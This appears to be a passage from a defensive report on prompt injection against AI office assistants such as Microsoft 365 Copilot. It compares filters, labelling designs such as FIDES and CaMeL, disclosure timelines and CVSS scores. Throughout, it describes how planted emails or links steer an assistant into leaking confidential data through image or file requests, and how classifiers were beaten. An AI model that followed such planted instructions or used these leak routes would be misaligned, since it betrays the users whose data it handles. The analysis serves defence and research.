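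Nasr and colleagues say the version of Spotlighting they tested uses delimiters, which Hines and colleagues had already advised against, so their result doesn't show how well datamarking or encoding would have worked. LLMail-Inject used a stronger version that replaces spaces with random strings, but about half the teams still got past it on the profit-forecast task.

Nasr and colleagues also tested whether anyone could break each defence, not how hard that would be. An outsider emailing a company would not see a classifier's score, but they could buy a Copilot licence, send emails to their own mailbox and keep rewriting them until one worked. The competition's participants also had limited information and feedback, and together they broke every defence they attacked.

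### The figures in 2026 system cards

AI developers now publish prompt injection test results for new models in system cards, which describe a model's tests and risks. The results are much better than those from 2025, but developers use different tests and count repeated attempts differently.

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that the model resisted 99.79 per cent of indirect injections in internal tests, up from 96.23 per cent for GPT-5.6 Sol. The attacks came from GPT-Red, an automated attacker that OpenAI also uses in training, so Astra had probably been trained against similar ones. Gray Swan, an outside firm, tested the models with 1,810 attacks collected earlier in 2026. It estimated that at least one of 15 attempts at a scenario would succeed 8.5 per cent of the time against Astra and 27.0 per cent of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol.

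How well a model resists malicious instructions depends heavily on the setting, according to Anthropic figures reported by VentureBeat. In February 2026, Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding test. When the same model controlled a computer through its screen, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 per cent of the time. The chance of at least one success in 200 attempts was 78.6 per cent, or 57.1 per cent with extra safeguards.

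Digital Applied (2026) cites a later result from Anthropic's card for Claude Fable 5, in which adaptive attacks on coding tasks succeeded 0.41 per cent of the time, compared with 2.09 per cent for Claude Opus 4.8. Anthropic also reported in June that Mythos 5, the less restricted version of the same model, had the best result yet on a Gray Swan injection benchmark. It has since announced a successor in *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (Anthropic, 2026).

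| Model | What the test measured | Could attackers retry? | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Astra | Indirect attacks by OpenAI's own program | Result is an average per query | 0.21% |
| GPT-6 Astra | Gray Swan attacks on coding, tools and computer use | Up to 15 attempts | 8.5% |
| Claude Fable 5 | Adaptive attacks on coding | 200 attempts per scenario | 0.41% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Control of a computer screen, no extra safeguards | 1 attempt, then 200 | 17.8%, then 78.6% |
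| Gemini 2.5 | Theft through a calendar entry | Thousands of practice queries | 94.6% |

The Gemini figure is from May 2025, so it doesn't show whether Google's current models are better or worse than its competitors'. How good the Fable 5 figure is depends on what it counts. If 0.41 per cent is the share of individual attempts that succeed, 200 independent attempts would have a 56 per cent chance of producing at least one success. If it is the share of scenarios in which any attempt succeeds, the result would be far more impressive.

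None of these tests used Microsoft 365 Copilot with a company's mailbox. The tests closest to an office copilot are those that deliver the attack through tools or outside content. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 did worse on these than on tests where the instructions were typed directly into a chat.

### Why 99 per cent is not enough

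Suppose a filter stops 99 per cent of malicious emails and an attacker sends 100 different ones. If the outcomes are independent, the chance that the filter stops them all is 0.99^100, or about 37 per cent, so the chance that at least one gets through is about 63 per cent. The table repeats the calculation for other success rates and numbers of emails.

| Share of attacks stopped | 10 emails | 100 emails | 1,000 emails |
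|---|---|---|---|
| 90% | 65% | Over 99.9% | Over 99.9% |
| 99% | 10% | 63% | Over 99.9% |
| 99.9% | 1% | 10% | 63% |

Real attempts are not independent. A classifier will normally give the same score to 100 copies of one email, so sending more copies gains the attacker nothing. The Opus 4.6 results also show that some targets are harder than others. If each attempt had an independent 17.8 per cent chance of success, 20 attempts would succeed at least once 98 per cent of the time. The measured rate was only 78.6 per cent after 200 attempts, evidently because in some scenarios nearly every attempt failed.

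The formula can also overstate how well the filter protects. An attacker who has found an email that passes can send it to every employee, and the filter will probably miss it each time. Shi and colleagues consider such reusable attacks the most worrying kind, because one cheap piece of text can target many people. They found that developing a highly successful one against Gemini 2.0 Flash cost less than $10.

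Getting past the filter is still only the first step of a theft.

### What false alarms do to ordinary mail

A company could make its filter stricter, but nearly all the mail it screens is harmless. If 2,000 employees each receive 50 outside emails a day, the filter screens 100,000 emails daily. If an attacker adds ten malicious ones, a filter that catches 99 per cent of attacks will flag about ten of them.

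| False-alarm rate | Harmless emails flagged per day | Share of alerts that are real attacks |
|---|---|---|
| 5% | 5,000 | 0.2% |
| 1% | 1,000 | 1% |
| 0.1% | 100 | 9% |
| 0.01% | 10 | 50% |

At a false-alarm rate of 1 per cent, which Shi and colleagues call high, a security team would have to check about 100 harmless emails for each malicious one, and would soon stop checking. The LLM judge that did so well in LLMail-Inject flagged 5 per cent of the Enron emails, which would mean 5,000 false alarms a day in this example. The text classifier raised no false alarms on 1,000 emails, but its true rate could still be up to about 0.3 per cent, or 300 a day.

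The harm from wrongly flagging an email depends on what the software does with it. If the software only keeps the email out of Copilot's context, the employee can still read it in the inbox, so the mistake does less harm than a spam filter hiding the message. But the finance director's summary of the merger might then omit the other side's latest offer, with no sign that anything is missing.

### How far to rely on them

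Filters and training are worth having because they stop crude attacks. LLMail-Inject suggests that they also force attackers to make far more attempts and settle for weaker instructions. Nasr and colleagues broke every detector they tried, but still call detectors useful as one part of a defence. David C adds that attackers will probably have to refine an attack, so a company that logs failed tool calls may notice the early attempts. This helps only if the attacker practises on the company's own assistant, because practising on a private account leaves nothing in the company's logs, although Microsoft might see it.

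The case against relying on them is stronger. Aim Labs got past Microsoft's classifier in 2025, and Cato did so three more times in 2026, after Microsoft had a year to improve it. A patient attacker would choose a mailbox that holds merger terms, so a defence that fails against such an attacker is a poor fit for that mailbox.

David C's comparison with SQL injection suggests that better filters may not solve prompt injection. SQL injection was at its worst around 2010, when many websites depended on databases and few had adopted parameterised queries. It is now rare because parameterised queries removed its cause, whereas filters, marking and training all leave the cause of prompt injection in place. David C is especially wary of lists of forbidden phrases, since an attacker can reword a sentence in endless ways, and of any product that claims to "stop" prompt injection. David C suggests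 that a task may not suit a language model if the organisation cannot accept the remaining risk.

Shi and colleagues at Google similarly say that developers should never rely on the company's training alone. They recommend combining it with systems such as CaMeL, which treat the model as untrusted and limit what it can do after an attack has succeeded.

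## Designs that stop a misdirected assistant from leaking data

If the stranger's email gets past every filter and the model follows its instructions, the software around the model can still keep the merger terms from leaving the company. That software can track where each piece of text came from and who may read it, and refuse certain actions on those grounds alone.

In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) argue that once an assistant has read untrusted text, that text must be unable to trigger a harmful action. They think it unlikely that a general-purpose assistant can reliably meet this standard with today's kind of language model, so each of their designs limits what the assistant can do.

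### Labels that travel with the text

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and uses fixed rules, not the model, to control where the data may go. Security researchers have studied it since the 1970s. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies it to AI assistants in a Microsoft research system called FIDES.

FIDES gives each piece of text two labels. The integrity label is T (trusted) or U (untrusted), depending on whether an attacker could have tampered with the text. The secrecy label lists who may read the text.

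When the model writes something new, the software can't work out which parts of the context influenced it, so it assumes that all of them did. It combines their labels as follows:

- The new text is trusted only if every input was trusted, so T combined with U gives U.
- Only people who could read every input may read the new text. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a summary of both.

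Two rules then govern what the assistant may do. Under the trust rule, it may take a consequential action, such as making a payment, only if the decision to act and the details of the action come from trusted text. Under the reader rule, it may send data somewhere only if everyone who would receive it is on the data's list of permitted readers. Neither rule depends on recognising a malicious instruction.

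### A refused image, step by step

In the merger example, the finance director asks Copilot where the negotiations stand. The search returns the confidential draft agreement and the stranger's email. The table traces the labels. An email's readers are its sender and recipients, as in Costa and colleagues' work.

| Text | Integrity | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The director's question | Trusted | Anyone |
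| The draft agreement | Trusted | Director, chief executive, company lawyer |
| Context with the question and the draft | Trusted | Director, chief executive, company lawyer |
| The stranger's email | Untrusted | Stranger, director |
| Context with the email added | Untrusted | Director |
| Copilot's answer | Untrusted | Director |

The model follows the instructions in the email and ends its answer with an image whose address contains the price. Loading the image would send the price to whoever runs the server at that address. The trust rule forbids loading it because the answer is untrusted, and the reader rule forbids it because the server's owner is not the director. The software leaves out the image, and the director still gets the written summary.

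Having both rules helps when somebody makes a mistake. In EchoLeak, the browser sent the data to a Teams address. An administrator might reasonably have listed Teams among the services that may receive company data. The reader rule would then have allowed the request, but the trust rule would still have stopped it.

FIDES as published would probably have missed EchoLeak, however, because by default it checks only tool calls and treats answers to the user as harmless. Costa and colleagues say that it can also check answers in settings where they are not harmless. An office copilot that displays images needs this stricter version.

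### Keeping outside text away from the planner

Labels can only get stricter as a conversation goes on, so once a single outside email enters the context, the trust rule would stop the assistant from sending a message or booking a meeting until the user starts a new conversation.

FIDES avoids much of this by hiding text from the model that plans the work. When a tool returns text that would make the context's label stricter, the software stores the text in a variable and gives the planning model only the variable's name. If the user asks for a summary of three emails to go to a colleague on Slack, the steps are:

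1. The planning model requests the emails and receives a name that stands for their text.
2. It asks a separate reading model, which has no tools, to summarise whatever that name stands for. The software stores the summary in another variable.
3. It calls the Slack tool with the name of the summary, and the software fills in the text.

The user decided to send the message and chose its recipient, so both decisions remain trusted. A planted instruction could make the summary wrong or empty, but could not send it to someone else.

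For some tasks, the planning model needs information from the emails, such as whether any of them contains a meeting request. FIDES can then restrict the reading model to a yes-or-no answer. Such an answer has little room for an instruction, so a company could allow the assistant to act on it. The planning model can also open the variable and read all of its contents, but the context then becomes untrusted.

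### CaMeL: a plan written before reading

Google DeepMind's CaMeL (2025) separates planning from reading more strictly. Like FIDES, it builds on the Dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in April 2023. In that pattern, one model has tools but never receives outside text, and a second model, which has no tools, reads that text.

*CaMeLoT* (2026), a paper on a successor to CaMeL, describes how the original system works. The planning model receives only the user's request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. An ordinary software interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. It passes outside text to the reading model and stores each result with a record of where it came from and who may read it.

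Suppose the director asks the assistant to summarise the other side's latest email and send the summary to the company's lawyer. The program finds the email, has the reading model summarise it and sends the result to the lawyer's address. If the email contains an instruction to send the draft agreement to a stranger, the draft is not sent, because the program has no step for sending it and the planning model never receives the email.

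The director might instead ask the assistant to send the draft to "the address in their latest email". If an attacker had written that email, they could choose the address, and the program would run as planned but send the draft to the wrong recipient. Separating the two models doesn't prevent this, but CaMeL also keeps a record that the address came from an outside email. As TechSpot explains, the interpreter can then block the action or ask the user to confirm it.

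Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, point out that CaMeL's plan cannot depend on what the tools return. CaMeL is therefore poorly suited to requests such as "deal with whatever this email asks for", which are also the most dangerous kind. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, tested ten defences against attacks that adapted to them, and found that attacks succeeded much more often when the user let the content determine the assistant's actions. Some designs that restrict the assistant's actions still resisted these attacks, but most of the ten defences were either insecure or substantially reduced the assistant's function.

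### What the guarantees cost in completed tasks

Researchers usually measure how much these designs reduce task completion with AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates an office workspace, travel booking, banking and Slack. It has 97 ordinary tasks and attacks planted in the data those tasks use. Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on it with GPT-4o, pairing each task with every attack in the same setting. They measured task completion separately, without attacks.

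| System | Successful attacks | Workspace tasks | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average of the four |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary assistant | 152 | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% | 84% |
| Ordinary assistant with the rules | 0 | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% | 42% |
| FIDES without the rules | 21 | 64% | 50% | 65% | 64% | 61% |
| FIDES with the rules | 0 | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% | 50% |

The attack figures exclude cases that Costa and colleagues inspected and judged not to be real successes. The third row shows that hiding text is not enough, because the planning model sometimes opened a variable and followed the instructions in it.

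Costa and colleagues report that FIDES completes 8 per cent more tasks than a basic assistant under the same rules. However, its completion rate was on average 34 percentage points lower than that of an unprotected assistant.

Part of that loss should shrink as models improve. GPT-4o often confused the variables' names or made unnecessary calls, and replacing it with OpenAI's o1 raised FIDES's score from 41 to 68 per cent on the travel tasks. The rest of the loss is deliberate, because many of the banking tasks involve reading a file and doing what it says, which the rules are meant to prevent.

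Kolluri and colleagues, also mostly from Microsoft, argue that this comparison is unfair to FIDES. Many real assistants ask for approval before any consequential action, so the unprotected assistant's score is realistic only if someone is always there to approve. They counted the tasks an assistant could finish without asking anyone. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an ordinary assistant finished 24 per cent, the same assistant with labels and rules 36 per cent, and FIDES 50 per cent. Their own system, Prudentia, finished 59 per cent. It builds on FIDES but also gives the planning model the labels and rules, so that it can choose a plan that won't break them.

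This is a good argument about actions such as sending email, where Copilot already asks for approval. It matters less for EchoLeak and SearchLeak, where data left through image requests that nobody was approving.

Estimates of how much CaMeL reduces an assistant's ability to complete tasks differ widely. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports a rerun on AgentDojo in which none of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. The paper's own rival design completed 59 and allowed slightly more attacks. The rerun adapted CaMeL's published code to another test setup, which may have caused it to fail some tasks. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to teams of agents, calls the loss in AgentDojo evaluations "comparatively modest", while Kolluri and colleagues put it at up to 30 per cent for designs of this kind. *ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower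 than filters or changes to the prompt, because its programs are longer than an ordinary choice of tool.

### Simpler patterns

A developer can get some of this protection without labels. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe six patterns, two of which correspond to the Dual LLM design and CaMeL.

| Pattern | How it works | What an attacker can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never receives their results | Nothing through retrieved text |
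| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of actions before reading anything | Change the contents of those actions, such as the text of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a limited answer, such as yes or no | Falsify the answer about one document |
| Dual LLM | A model without tools reads outside text for the planning model | Alter the text that the reading model returns |
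| Code, then execute | The model writes a program that calls the tools and reading models | Alter the text that the program handles |
| Context minimisation | The software deletes the user's prompt before the model writes the answer | Plant instructions in the retrieved text |

An action selector would be almost useless as an office copilot because it could not summarise an email. For an assistant that handles email and calendars, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider the plan-then-execute, Dual LLM and code-then-execute patterns. They expect the assistant to lose little function, because the order of its steps seldom needs to depend on what a stranger wrote.

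They also identify a gap in those patterns. If the user asks for a reply to the attacker's email, the plan properly includes a message to the attacker. Hidden instructions could then make the model add confidential material to that message in invisible characters. The reader rule would stop this, but it would also stop the director from deliberately sending the other side a figure from the draft, unless the director approved the exception.

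Context minimisation deals with malicious prompts from the user. It can matter even for an assistant that works for its own user, because an attacker may supply the prompt, as SearchLeak's attacker did through a link. If the software had turned that prompt into a search and then deleted it, the model would no longer have had the instruction to put an email's title in an image address. However, users would also have been unable to say how they wanted the answer laid out.

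### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the lethal trifecta into a limit on each session. An assistant may combine any two of untrusted input, private data and outside communication, but it may combine all three only if a person supervises it or another reliable check is in place. Meta groups the power to change anything with outside communication.

Meta gives three ways for an assistant that manages an inbox to comply. The assistant could read mail only from trusted senders, work without access to private data, or send only messages that go to trusted recipients or that a person has checked. It can also switch between these arrangements partway through a task. For example, an assistant could research a company on the web, then permanently lose its outside connection before opening a draft agreement with that company.

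Developers can apply the rule without rebuilding the assistant, but only if they know everything that counts as communication. Before EchoLeak, a developer could honestly have described Copilot's answers as private to the user. The travel assistant in Meta's example is fairly well protected against this type of leak because it may visit only web addresses from trusted sources, not ones it has put together itself. Meta adds that a design can follow the rule and still fail, such as when a user approves a warning without reading it.

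Some narrower measures each remove all or part of one of the properties. One is to exclude outside mail from the search, at least in any session that uses internal files. Checking the sender's address is not quite enough, because a trusted colleague may forward a stranger's text. Another is to load no remote content when displaying an answer. Users would lose little except pictures from other sites.

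The third is to run code in a sandbox with no internet connection. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues report that sandboxing a data-analysis assistant's code causes no loss of function. That makes it one of the least restrictive protections available, as long as the isolation holds better than it did in ReLeak.

### Asking the user

Many of these designs ask the user when a rule would block something. This works best for actions the user expected to check anyway, such as sending an email that Copilot has drafted. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think the burden of answering these requests is low at a desk but much higher for someone talking to an assistant through a watch or phone. Even a careful user could miss data hidden in invisible characters.

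Approval requests protect users less as they become more frequent. Kolluri and colleagues tested assistants on simulated versions of GitLab and Reddit, where the user's task was only to post a comment or upvote a post. On GitLab, an ordinary assistant needed about three approvals per task. People who face this many requests stop reading them, which researchers call confirmation fatigue. An attack can then succeed when a distracted user approves it.

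Prudentia completed the same kind of task without needing any approvals, and none of the attacks succeeded. It never had to open the text that other people had posted, so its context stayed trusted and the rules had nothing to block.

When Prudentia has to read outside text, it can ask the user to vouch for the text once instead of approving each action, so an email with ten items to carry out needs only one question. But vouching for the email also covers anything in it that the user can't see, such as white text on a white background. The trust rule will no longer restrain that hidden text. Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of these questions to later work, but suggest showing where the data came from and how it is labelled. Showing the text exactly as the model will receive it would also help.

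### The designs against the known attacks

The table compares the main designs against four routes that attackers have used on Microsoft 365 Copilot. The entries are inferred from how each attack worked, not from tests on Copilot.

| Design | EchoLeak: image through Teams | SearchLeak: prompt in a link, image through Bing | ReLeak: saved file | ReLeak: Python code | Function lost |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
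| Labels with both rules | Stops the image, if the rules cover answers | Stops the image, if the rules cover answers | Stops the save, unless saving is exempt | Stops the code, unless running code is exempt | Acting on outside mail without approval |
| CaMeL | Needs a rule for displaying answers | The plan itself comes from the attacker, so needs the same rule | No such step in the plan unless the user asked for a file | No such step unless the task needed code | Tasks whose steps depend on an email |
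| Rule of Two, with no outside communication | Stops the image, if the vendor counts it | Stops the image, if the vendor counts it | Stops the server's request, if the vendor counts it | Stops the code's request | Sending anything without approval |
| No outside mail alongside internal files | Keeps the email out | No effect | Keeps the email out | Keeps the email out | Comparing an outside offer with an internal draft |
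| No remote content in answers | Stops the image but not a clicked link | Stops the image | No effect | No effect | Pictures from other sites |
| Closed sandbox | No effect | No effect | No effect | Stops the request, if the isolation holds | Code that needs live data |
| Approval by the user | The user sees a Teams address | The user sees a Bing address | The user sees an ordinary file | The user sees code that few can read | Time and attention |

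SearchLeak is the hardest case for designs that trust the user, because the product treated the attacker's prompt as the user's own. Kolluri and colleagues exclude direct prompt injection from the attacks Prudentia defends against. They also let an assistant send data out if the action satisfies either the trust rule or the reader rule, reasoning that a trusted user who sends a secret to an outsider presumably means to. If the link's text had been labelled as trusted, that policy would have let SearchLeak through. A vendor could require both rules for anything that loads automatically, or label text from links as untrusted. The second option is simple and would also help against Reprompt and CoSnitch.

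The results in the ReLeak columns depend on which actions a vendor exempts. People often ask an assistant to read some emails and save a summary as a Word file. The trust rule would forbid this, so a vendor would be tempted to classify saving as harmless. The reader rule would allow it, because the file goes into the user's own folder. Microsoft's servers would then process the file and contact the attacker's address, as they did in ReLeak. A vendor could likewise exempt Python code in the belief that the sandbox has no network connection. The safest fix is to attach the labels to the file and apply the reader rule again before a server fetches anything for it.

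Loading no remote content and blocking requests from file processing would together have closed three of the four routes by which data left, with hardly any loss to users. Keeping outside mail apart from internal files stops three of the four attacks earlier, but it also prevents the assistant from using both together, which a finance director working on a merger would need every day.

### Adding labels to a product that already exists

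In its guide for developers, Microsoft recommends information-flow control and advises them to consider prompt injection while designing the user interface, prompts and architecture. It warns of added complexity and of delays from running a separate reading model. In 2025 Microsoft described FIDES and the design patterns as part of the foundation for its next generation of defences.

In the AgentDojo results, adding the rules to an ordinary assistant without changing how it planned halved average task completion. FIDES and Prudentia recovered part of the loss, but only by redesigning the planner. This suggests that a vendor that waits, then adds the rules without redesigning the planner, gets the security but loses the most function.

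Someone also has to supply the labels. The AgentDojo benchmark has none, so Costa and colleagues wrote software around each tool to add them. They marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. That was a reasonable way to get a clear baseline, but a company doesn't have a list of where attacks will come from.

An existing copilot would need labels on mail, files, chats, saved memories and records from connected services, and checks everywhere data can leave. Different teams usually own these parts. A team that starts with labels can refuse to connect a new data source until it has them, but a team that adds them later has to decide how to treat years of unlabelled documents. If it treats them all as untrusted, the assistant can do very little. If it treats them all as trusted, an attacker's instructions in an old supplier's brochure could misdirect the assistant.

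CaMeL is even harder to add because it replaces the part of the assistant that chooses and runs actions. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) left CaMeL out of one of its two comparisons for this reason. The test setup could only put a generic stand-in where the model would be, which would have replaced the interpreter and policies that make up CaMeL's defence.

Products can adopt these designs in stages. The integrity filtering that GitHub Next describes applies labels to one type of agent and a limited set of places it can write to. An office copilot could similarly start with the channels that send data out automatically and leave most of its other functions unchanged.

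### Where labels and policies still fail

If a label is wrong, the rules can fail without any visible sign. Costa and colleagues infer who can read an email from its addresses, although somebody may since have shared it more widely. They also mention that a system could relabel an untrusted document as trusted after a classifier has passed it. This would let the assistant do more, but the guarantee would be only as reliable as the classifier, and attackers have repeatedly beaten such classifiers.

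Labels can also get lost when text moves. If Copilot saves a note from an untrusted page to its memory without the label, the system will later treat the note as trusted. Output from a sandbox can lose its label too. In ChatMate, the attacker's messages reached Copilot as the output of a program running on Microsoft's own servers, which a carelessly written policy might have marked as trusted.

Even with perfect labels, FIDES controls only data that the assistant sends directly. Costa and colleagues call this property explicit secrecy and acknowledge that an attacker who can see which tools the assistant calls may still learn something from its choices. Bargury's attack on Copilot revealed a yes-or-no answer in a similar way, through Copilot's choice between two links. The software could rule out such leaks only by forbidding almost any outside action after the assistant had handled confidential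 data, which Costa and colleagues consider too restrictive. The guarantee also doesn't cover information leaked through timing or message size.

The designs also assume that the tools and their descriptions are trustworthy. That assumption failed in PromptArmor's attack on Copilot Cowork, because the user had installed the attacker's script as a Skill.

Finally, the rules restrict what an assistant does with data but don't ensure that its answers are true. A planted email could still make Copilot report that the other side had accepted a condition it had refused, and the director might sign because of that report.

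## How the flaws are reported, scored and patched

A vendor that hasn't rebuilt its assistant around labels and fixed rules has to repair flaws one at a time, usually after outside researchers find them. Researchers normally tell the vendor privately and publish only once the flaw is fixed, a practice called coordinated disclosure. Aim disclosed EchoLeak this way, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025).

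### One report from start to finish

Copirate 365, Rehberger's attack through Copilot's HTML preview, has an unusually full public timeline. Most of the dates below come from Embrace The Red, but the two about the CVE number come from the official record, MITRE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026).

| Date | Step |
|---|---|
| 16 October 2025 | Rehberger reports that background images and fonts can carry data out |
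| 18 October | Microsoft's Security Response Center opens a case |
| 12 November | Microsoft confirms that it can reproduce the attack |
| 17 December | Microsoft awards a bounty |
| 21 January 2026 | Microsoft reserves a CVE number |
| 25 February | The fix is reaching customers |
| 5 March | Microsoft marks the case as resolved |
| 19 March | Microsoft publishes the CVE |

Microsoft needed 27 days to reproduce the attack and another 113 to fix it. Rehberger added to his report in the meantime. Four days after filing it, he realised that the content security policy differed between the programs that host Copilot, and in November he sent a version of the attack that planted a lasting memory. He filed five tickets in all. Microsoft fixed the memory flaw in early December, three months before it blocked the route by which data could leave.

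### Why cloud flaws had no number

The CVE system dates from 1999, when most software ran on customers' own machines. Companies needed a shared name for each flaw so they could check whether they had installed the right update. Flaws in cloud services didn't fit this purpose, because the provider fixes them. Microsoft's *Toward greater transparency* (2024) acknowledges that cloud providers used to say nothing about flaws they had fixed unless customers had to act.

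Wiz's *Increasing transparency in cloud security* repeats the security firm's 2021 complaint that cloud flaws had no identifiers or severity scores, and that there was no proper way to notify customers about them. It cites a flaw in Microsoft's Cosmos DB database service. Customers had to replace their access keys themselves and couldn't tell how long they had been exposed. Data Center Knowledge's *Microsoft* reports a similar complaint from Amit Yoran, then head of the security firm Tenable, who accused Microsoft of "silently" patching a flaw in its Azure cloud and playing down the risk.

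In June 2024 Microsoft announced that it would issue CVEs for critical flaws in its cloud services, whether or not customers had to act. The CVE programme had recently revised its rules to say that a vendor should publish a flaw if it could cause significant harm, or if anyone else needed to act on it or assess the risk. Microsoft stressed that either condition was enough. It also began to tag these cloud-service records so that administrators who care only about installing updates can filter them out. EchoLeak's record, as reproduced by the vulnerability database GCVE (2025), has this tag.

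The promise covers only flaws that Microsoft rates as critical. Microsoft also assigns the CVE numbers for flaws in its own products, so it could still fix a less severe Copilot flaw without leaving a public record. Even so, the policy has made many fixes public. Rewterz's *Critical Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaws Expose Data* (2026) lists three flaws disclosed on one day in May 2026, none of which required customers to do anything.

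The official records contain very little information. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the entry for SearchLeak, has the same title and one-sentence description as the entry for Copirate 365. The description is of "command injection" that lets an attacker disclose information over a network. An administrator with only these records could not tell that one attack used a font and the other a link. Nearly all the useful information about either flaw comes from the people who found it.

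### What the bug bounties pay for

Vendors pay researchers for reports through bug bounty programmes, whose rules define which flaws qualify. In 2025 Microsoft's Copilot bounty offered $250 to $30,000. It excluded prompt injections that affect only the attacker and tricks that only reveal Copilot's hidden system instructions. Logue received nothing for the Mermaid diagram attack because Microsoft considered Microsoft 365 Copilot out of scope. In December 2025 Microsoft brought all its online services into scope by default, and Rehberger received his award the same month.

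Google opened a separate programme for AI flaws in October 2025. It offered up to $20,000 for a flaw in a leading product such as Search, Gemini or Gmail, or up to $30,000 with bonuses for an exceptional report. The programme pays for attacks that make an assistant leak someone's data or take a harmful action on their account. It excludes jailbreaks and direct prompt injection, which Google asks people to report through the product's feedback button.

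These exclusions are mostly sensible. Someone who gets their own assistant to say something rude has stolen nothing, and a vendor could spend its whole budget on such reports. But the rules tie the reward to a completed theft. A researcher who shows that a stranger's email can steer Copilot has found the more basic weakness, but is unlikely to be paid much until they also find a way to get data out. Rehberger's first report on invisible characters ran into this problem in 2024. Vendors therefore receive reports that each focus on a particular way of getting data out, which may be one reason they patch those routes.

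### How long the repairs took

The table gives the time from report to fix for the main Copilot flaws. Where only a month or a range is public, the last column shows the shortest and longest possible intervals.

| Flaw | Reported | Fixed | Days to fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | January 2025 | May 2025 | 90–150 |
| Mermaid diagrams | 15 August 2025 | By 26 September 2025 | 42 at most |
| Reprompt | 31 August 2025 | 13 January 2026 | 135 |
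| Copirate 365 | 16 October 2025 | 5 March 2026 | 140 |
| CoSnitch | December 2025 | 18 August 2026 | 230–260 |
| SearchLeak | Not public | By 4 June 2026 | Unknown |
| ReLeak: Python code | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September 2026 | 28–50 |
| ReLeak: saved file | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 11 November 2026 | 83–105 |
| ReLeak: image through Bing | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 15 November 2026 | 87–109 |

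The ReLeak dates come from Faisal, who gives a single reporting window for all three flaws. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) gives the same repair dates and credits them to the news site BleepingComputer. The Reprompt patch date comes from Windows Central (2026), and the August date is when Taler's firm reported the flaw.

Varonis has not said when it reported SearchLeak. Microsoft reserved the CVE number on 30 April 2026 and published it on 4 June, so by then it had probably known about the flaw for at least five weeks.

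CoSnitch took the longest to fix, at about eight months. Microsoft partly repaired the flaw, which Varonis had reported, in February 2026 without announcing it. None of the published accounts explains what that repair covered or why the rest took six more months.

Google's security research team, Project Zero, normally gives vendors 90 days to fix a flaw before publishing it. Reprompt, Copirate 365 and CoSnitch all took much longer to fix, and the attacks presumably worked for most of that time. Other vendors have been quicker. Salesforce fixed ForcedLeak in 42 days, and Slack and Notion each released a fix within a day of PromptArmor publishing its findings. These cases suggest that publicity speeds up fixes, but they are too few to show that Microsoft could safely have worked as fast. Microsoft also has to make any change to Copilot work in Word, Excel, Outlook, Teams and the browser.

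Of the three ReLeak routes, Microsoft closed the Python sandbox first and Bing last, which is odd because it had dealt with a leak through Bing only a few months earlier. The order may reflect severity, or a network restriction in a sandbox may be easier to change than a public search engine that fetches pictures for everybody.

### Why the scores disagree

A CVSS score combines a handful of judgements about a flaw. Under version 3.1, which Microsoft used for these flaws, the scorer first decides how easy the attack is. Can the attacker strike over a network? Does the attack depend on conditions outside the attacker's control? Does the attacker need an account, and does a victim have to do something? Each answer has a fixed weight, and the formula multiplies them:

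exploitability = 8.22 × vector × complexity × privileges × interaction

The scorer then rates the loss of confidentiality, integrity and availability. If only confidentiality suffers, and the harm stays within the component that has the flaw, the rest of the calculation is simple:

impact = 6.42 × confidentiality

score = exploitability + impact, rounded up to one decimal place

For SearchLeak, Microsoft's answers give 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.62, or 2.84. The 0.62 is the weight for an attack that needs the victim to act. A high loss of confidentiality has a weight of 0.56, which makes the impact 3.60. The two add up to 6.43, which rounds up to a score of 6.5. If the victim didn't have to act, the 0.62 would be 0.85 and the score would be 7.5.

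That answer explains the first dispute. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* reports that the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD), which makes its own assessments, gave SearchLeak 7.5 because it assumed that no user interaction was needed. Microsoft is right that interaction was needed, since the victim had to click a link.

The next table shows the answers that differ. In every row the attack comes over a network, the attacker needs no account, the loss of confidentiality is high and availability is unaffected.

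| Flaw | Scorer | Complexity | User interaction | Scope | Loss of integrity | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Microsoft | Low | None | Changed | Low | 9.3 |
| EchoLeak | NVD | Low | None | Unchanged | None | 7.5 |
| SearchLeak | Microsoft | Low | Required | Unchanged | None | 6.5 |
| SearchLeak | NVD | Low | None | Unchanged | None | 7.5 |
| Copirate 365 | Microsoft | High | Required | Unchanged | None | 5.3 |

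"Scope" in CVSS describes whether a flaw in one component harms something under another component's control. It is unrelated to Ravia's term "LLM scope violation". Microsoft judged that EchoLeak did cause such harm, and that it also caused a small loss of integrity. The scope rating alone raises the score from 7.5 to 8.6, and adding the integrity rating raises it to 9.3.

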